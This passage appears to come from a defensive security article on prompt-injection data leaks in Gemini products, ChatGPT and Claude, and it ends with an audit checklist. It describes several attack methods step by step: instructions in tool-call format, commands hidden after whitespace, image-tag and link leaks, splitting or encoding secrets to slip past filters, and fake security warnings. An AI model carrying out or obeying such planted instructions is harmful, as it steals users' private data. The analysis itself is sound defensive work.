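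Lidzborski also recommended removing hidden text before the model receives it. That would delete the white text in the picnic email, but an attacker could still write the instructions in visible text.

The argument against input filters doesn't apply equally to Gemini's output filter. Lidzborski's own design removes images, checks links with Safe Browsing, and removes addresses that the model produced without a source. The image and source checks only need to detect an image or an unsourced address in the reply, without determining what an email is meant to make the model do. *Surviving the Perfect Storm*, the talk's companion page, advises designers to assume that any layer may fail and to make the layers overlap.

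Google has since combined both approaches in Workspace Studio, its tool for automating office tasks. *Defend against agentic risks with multi-layered protections in Google Workspace Studio* (Quinney, 2026) describes classifiers that stop an automation if planted instructions pull it away from its task. The defense includes a self-reflection step, but Quinney gives no figures for how well it withstands adaptive attacks.

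Studio also gives each automation only the permissions it needs. An automation that sends email through Gmail has no access to Drive, so a planted email can't make it read a Drive file even if every classifier fails. The automation could still read a gate code stored in Gmail, so administrators can require the owner's approval before an automation sends anything outside the organization. That protection again depends on the owner reading the request.

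## Where data has still got out, and why

Since Google began filtering Gemini's replies, researchers have kept finding ways to get data out of its AI products. In some cases a tool sent the data without displaying anything, and in others the product had no filter. An attacker can also persuade the user to act, or leak a secret slowly through links the filter permits.

### A tool made the request

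By the time Tenable studied Gemini in 2025, external images no longer appeared in its replies and links no longer worked as they once had, so the researchers looked for a tool that would contact a server by itself. Gemini's browsing tool fetches a web page for the model to summarize, and the model supplies the address.

Gemini refused a plain instruction to send a user's saved information (facts it remembers about them) to an outside website. But its "Show thinking" feature revealed the format it uses to call its browsing tool, so the researchers rewrote the instruction in that format, with a placeholder for the private data. Gemini filled in the placeholder and fetched the address, and the researchers' server recorded a mock victim's saved information.

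Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* says Gemini's browsing tool did not check the destination well enough or ask for confirmation. Tenable reported the flaw on 16 April 2025. Google said it was fixed on 18 June, five days after announcing its layered defenses. Google has described the fix only as preventing data exfiltration through browsing in indirect prompt injections, so outsiders can't tell whether the fix checks the address or restricts when the tool may run.

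To stop such leaks, a designer can reuse the link filter's address checks, but has to run them before each tool call.

SC Media, a security news site, describes a similar leak in Gemini CLI, Google's command-line assistant. The attack started with a harmless search command that a user would probably choose to "always allow". Further commands, placed after a run of blank spaces, sent private settings to an outside server and left no sign in the output. The security company Tracebit reported the flaw on 27 June 2025, and Google fixed it four weeks later.

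In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) measured this kind of leak in a deliberately vulnerable agent that used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, rather than Gemini. They placed a secret in the model's input and asked it to summarize web pages that contained planted instructions. Data leaked in 423 of 480 runs, or 88% (the abstract gives about 0.89). In 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server. The agent's final answer looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks, so checking only the answer would have missed them.

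The researchers then tested several defenses 30 times each. Telling the model to ignore instructions in web pages reduced the leak rate from 100% to 67%. Marking the page as untrusted data made no difference. A list of permitted domains stopped every leak, but the researchers had deliberately chosen an attacker domain that was not on it. They acknowledge that an attacker could get around the list through an open redirect on a permitted site.

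When Lan and colleagues switched on a filter that checks requests for random-looking strings, the agent never tried to send the secret. They suggest that the model avoids such strings when it is monitored. But the filter, as they describe it, examines a request only after the model has written it, so it's unclear why the model's behavior changed.

They also told the model to split the secret into four pieces and send each in a separate request. A filter that checks each request separately may find only four harmless-looking characters. The extra steps made the attack less reliable. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 60% to 90% of runs, depending on the setup, compared with 97% to 100% when it sent the secret whole.

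None of these rates should be applied to Gemini, because the researchers used a small model, gave it a minimal system prompt, and put the secret directly in its input. A finished product can also behave very differently from a bare model. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), a model reached through its programming interface leaked data in up to 100% of trials, while ChatGPT leaked in none of 48. The study could not determine which part of ChatGPT made the difference.

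### The product lacked the filter

The security company Noma found an image leak, which it called GeminiJack, affecting Gemini Enterprise, which searches a company's email, calendars and documents, and Vertex AI Search, a Google Cloud service for building search tools. Google's June 2025 announcement covered the Workspace assistant and the Gemini app but did not mention either of these products.

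Paganini (2025), in *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration*, reproduces Noma's account of the attack. The attacker shares a document, or sends an email or calendar invitation, with instructions to search the company's files for a word such as "acquisition". The instructions take effect when an employee searches for something related, such as budget plans, even if the employee never opens the attacker's document. Gemini Enterprise retrieves that document along with the genuine ones, follows its instructions and adds the search results to the address of an image, which the employee's browser then requests.

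The leak used an HTML image tag, the same channel Google had closed in AI Studio in 2024. Sasi Levi of Noma said in TechNadu's *New AI-Native Threat* that Google "didn't filter HTML output", and that Noma had extracted long emails this way.

News reports disagree about whether Noma reported the flaw to Google in May or June 2025, probably because Noma printed the date as 05/06/25. Even the later date, 5 June, is eight days before Google announced that EchoLeak did not apply to Gemini. A Gemini Enterprise customer could easily have assumed from that announcement that the product had the same protection.

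SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* reports that Google confirmed Noma's description and said it had mitigated the flaw. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* says that Google separated Vertex AI Search from Gemini Enterprise and changed how both interact with the systems that retrieve documents. SC Media's *Google addresses 'GeminiJack' exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* dates the fix to November 2025 and cites Levi as saying that Google had not disclosed the technical details. Google may also have started removing image tags. If it changed only the retrieval, new instructions that got past the change could use the same channel again.

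Antigravity, a code editor with a built-in AI agent, was released in November 2025 with similar gaps. Google based it on Windsurf, an existing editor whose code it had licensed for about $2.4 billion. Rehberger had reported several flaws to Windsurf in May 2025. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* shows that two of Windsurf's data leaks still worked in Antigravity. In one, the chat loaded an external image, and in the other, a tool for reading web pages sent out the contents of a file of passwords and keys without asking the user.

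The Gemini app had been blocking external images for at least five months by then. But that protection is in the software that handles the app's replies, so another product doesn't get it just by using a Gemini model.

PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack through a third channel, the browser that Antigravity's agent can operate. The browser could visit only domains on a permitted list, but Google's default list included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and read every request sent to it. Another setting was supposed to keep the agent out of the file containing the keys. The setting blocked the file-reading tool, so Gemini printed the file with a terminal command instead.

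Google did not treat these reports as new security bugs. Willison (2025) noted that Google had told one researcher that the image leak was "intended behavior". Google's page for bug reporters listed leaks through the browser agent as "known issues", which Google was working to fix but did not reward people for reporting. A discussion copied on Brian Lovin's website quotes the page on the agent's access to private files: "While it is cautious in accessing sensitive files, there's no enforcement." PromptArmor did not report its findings to Google because Google had already acknowledged the risk.

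Antigravity still loaded external images in June 2026. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) disguised instructions as an error log and put them in the title of an otherwise empty web page. The agent read a secret key from the computer's settings and placed it in an image address. Odson and Morris requested the image in five notations because only one had to get past a filter.

Antigravity asked the user for approval first, but it asked for permission to generate a "visual debug token" and showed neither the command nor the destination. The model had written that description, so the user approved something that sounded harmless. Odson and Morris report no response or fix from Google, and it is unclear whether Google has since fixed the leak.

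### The user clicks or believes the text

Gemini Cloud Assist helps engineers understand the logs of their Google Cloud services. These logs record details that visitors send, including their browser's name, which they can replace with any text. Tenable sent instructions this way without logging in. When an engineer asked Gemini to explain the log entry, the explanation included a phishing link. The interface hid the planted text unless the engineer expanded the details.

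According to Tenable's *Google Cloud Platform (GCP) Gemini Cloud Assist Prompt Injection Vulnerability* (2025), the company reported the vulnerability in December 2024 and Google had fixed it by 5 March 2025. Google now shows links in log summaries as markdown text that can't be clicked. This also blocks links to phishing sites that Safe Browsing has not yet detected. The change barely inconveniences engineers, because they can copy a link they need.

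Tenable found another one-click leak in a version of Gemini that used people's search history to personalize answers. A malicious website could make a visitor's browser start a Google search and interrupt it before the results loaded. The search still entered the visitor's history, where Gemini later treated it as an instruction. In the demonstration, the user typed "Hello" and Gemini replied with a link that contained the user's saved information and would send it to the attacker if clicked.

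Tenable reported the flaw on 4 April 2025 (*Gemini Search Personalization Model*, 2025). Google withdrew the vulnerable model and kept strengthening the feature until late July. A provenance check should have removed this link, because the model had composed the address. Yet only twelve days after reporting the flaw, Tenable wrote in its browsing-tool report that ordinary links were already restricted. Either the restriction was new, or it did not cover every feature.

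An attacker may not need a link. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes an email with invisible text that told Gemini to add a warning to its summary. The warning said that the user's Gmail password had been stolen and gave a phone number to call. Figueroa manages 0din, Mozilla's program for reporting flaws in AI systems. According to TechBriefly (2025), Google said it was strengthening its defenses and had seen no evidence of the attack in real use.

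A link filter can't catch such a warning because it contains no link. Checking that the phone number appears somewhere in the email wouldn't help either, because the attacker put it there. A stricter check could accept only numbers in text that the reader can see. Lidzborski and Figueroa both recommend deleting invisible text, and Figueroa also suggests scanning summaries for phone numbers and urgent security language. The scan would need care, since a legitimate email, such as one from a dentist, may give the reader a reason to call.

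The same trick can deliver a link. Startup Daily's *Scammers can now use Google Gemini for phishing as pretend AI* describes a reporter's test in which the false warning included links to active phishing sites. Earlier, in *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability Enabling Phishing & Content Manipulation*, Martin and Yeung (2024) made Gemini tell users to reset their password at a misspelled Google address. They replaced the dots with a similar-looking Arabic character so that software would not recognize the address as a link, though a person might still type it into a browser.

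Google closed Martin and Yeung's report as "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)". Android Authority describes a later report in which hidden text made Gemini recommend a malicious shopping site, and Google reportedly said this was not a security bug either. A team that relies on a vendor's list of fixed vulnerabilities may therefore miss attacks that work by deceiving the user.

### Permitted links can spell out a secret

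An attacker can leak a secret through links that a filter permits by preparing 36 web pages, one for each letter and digit. Planted instructions tell the model to visit the pages that match the secret's characters, and the attacker reads those characters from the server's log.

Each request for one of 36 pages leaks log2(36), or about 5.2, bits. A random 16-character secret made of letters and digits contains about 83 bits, so leaking it takes 16 requests. An attacker who prepares 1,296 pages, one for each pair of characters, needs only 8.

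Rehberger described an early form of this attack in 2023 and pointed out two difficulties for the attacker. Requests may arrive out of order, and a browser may reuse a saved copy of a page instead of requesting it again, so an attacker stealing the gate code 4471 might see only one 4. Embrace The Red suggests making the attack harder by saving each response for a few minutes or refusing to visit the same address twice in a session.

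Those measures would stop the simple version, but an attacker could prepare a separate set of 36 pages for each position in the secret, or 576 pages for 16 characters. No address would then repeat, and the order of arrival would not matter. A limit on the total number of requests would still slow this version down. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) reports that ChatGPT could open only ten addresses per prompt at the time, which limited a leak of one character at a time to ten characters.

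In July 2026 Willison wrote about a working version of this attack against Claude. A website displayed what looked like an alphabetical directory of user profiles, and Claude followed its links letter by letter, which gave the researchers the user's name, home city and employer. The site showed these pages only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the attack harder for anyone else to notice. Anthropic responded by stopping its web-fetching tool from following links found in pages it had fetched.

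ChatGPT automatically loads an address only if that exact address is in the index of OpenAI's crawler. The crawler has no access to conversations, so it is unlikely to have recorded an address containing a user's secret. For any other address, the system prompts the agent to try another website or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

OpenAI considered a list of trusted sites and found it insufficient, both because of redirects and because a strict list could produce so many warnings that people would learn to click through them. OpenAI promises only to prevent quiet leaks through the address itself, so its promise doesn't cover phishing or false content.

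Rehberger thinks this is a significant improvement but notes that an attacker's own pages can also be in the index. An ordinary blog may already have 36 indexed pages, and a larger site could have thousands. He also doubts that every team at OpenAI will apply the check. The ChatGPT apps for macOS and iOS lacked its earlier version, much as Gemini Enterprise and Antigravity lacked Google's image rule.

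Google argues that slow leaks can't easily steal much data if each one requires a click. This holds up well when the target is a password or a long document, because few people would click 16 strange links in a row. It is weaker for short secrets. One click among 10,000 prepared links can reveal a four-digit gate code, though an email with that many links would look suspicious. One click on either of two links can reveal whether a company is planning a merger, and an email with two links would not look suspicious.

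The argument also holds only if a person clicks the links. If a browsing tool or a messaging app's link preview opens them instead, the attacker can collect many characters without the user noticing.

### The cases compared

| Case | Channel | Did a link or image filter apply? | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini browsing tool | Web request by a tool | No. The tool bypassed the displayed reply. | Google blocked exfiltration through browsing in June 2025. |
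| Gemini CLI | Terminal command | No. The command contacted the server directly. | Google released a fixed version in July 2025. |
| GeminiJack | HTML image | No. The product did not filter HTML output. | Google changed document retrieval and separated the two products by November 2025. |
| Antigravity | External images, a web-reading tool and the agent's browser | Images loaded. The browser had a domain list, but it permitted a request-logging site. | Google listed known issues in November 2025. The image leak still worked in June 2026. |
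| Cloud Assist | Phishing link in a log summary | The link remained clickable. | Google stopped making links clickable in log summaries by March 2025. |
| Search history | Link containing saved information | The link remained clickable. | Google withdrew the model and strengthened the feature. |
| Gmail summary | False warning with a phone number | The warning contained no link to remove. | Google said it was strengthening its defenses. |
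| Claude's web tool | Choice among existing links | The tool allowed links from pages it had fetched. | Anthropic stopped the tool from following those links. |

### Checks for an audit

An auditor can run most of these checks with an invented secret and a test server, using the server's log to see whether anything got out:

- Ask for an external image in every product and app that displays the model's replies, including previews and side panels. Try inline markdown, reference-style markdown and HTML.
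- List every tool that can contact the internet, including the terminal, and try to send the secret through each one.
- Have the model put the secret in the path, the subdomain and the part after the question mark. Repeat the test with the secret in base64.
- For each permitted domain, find out whether an outsider can store data there, read its request logs or redirect visitors elsewhere. Include the company's own domains.
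- Post a reply containing a test link in each connected messaging app, and see whether a preview opens it before anyone clicks.
- Prepare 36 harmless pages and count how many the assistant will open in one conversation, with and without repeats.
- Put a false security warning in invisible text and ask for a summary. Use a phone number in one test and a misspelled web address in another.
- Trigger an approval request and compare it with the action that follows. It should show the exact command and the full destination.
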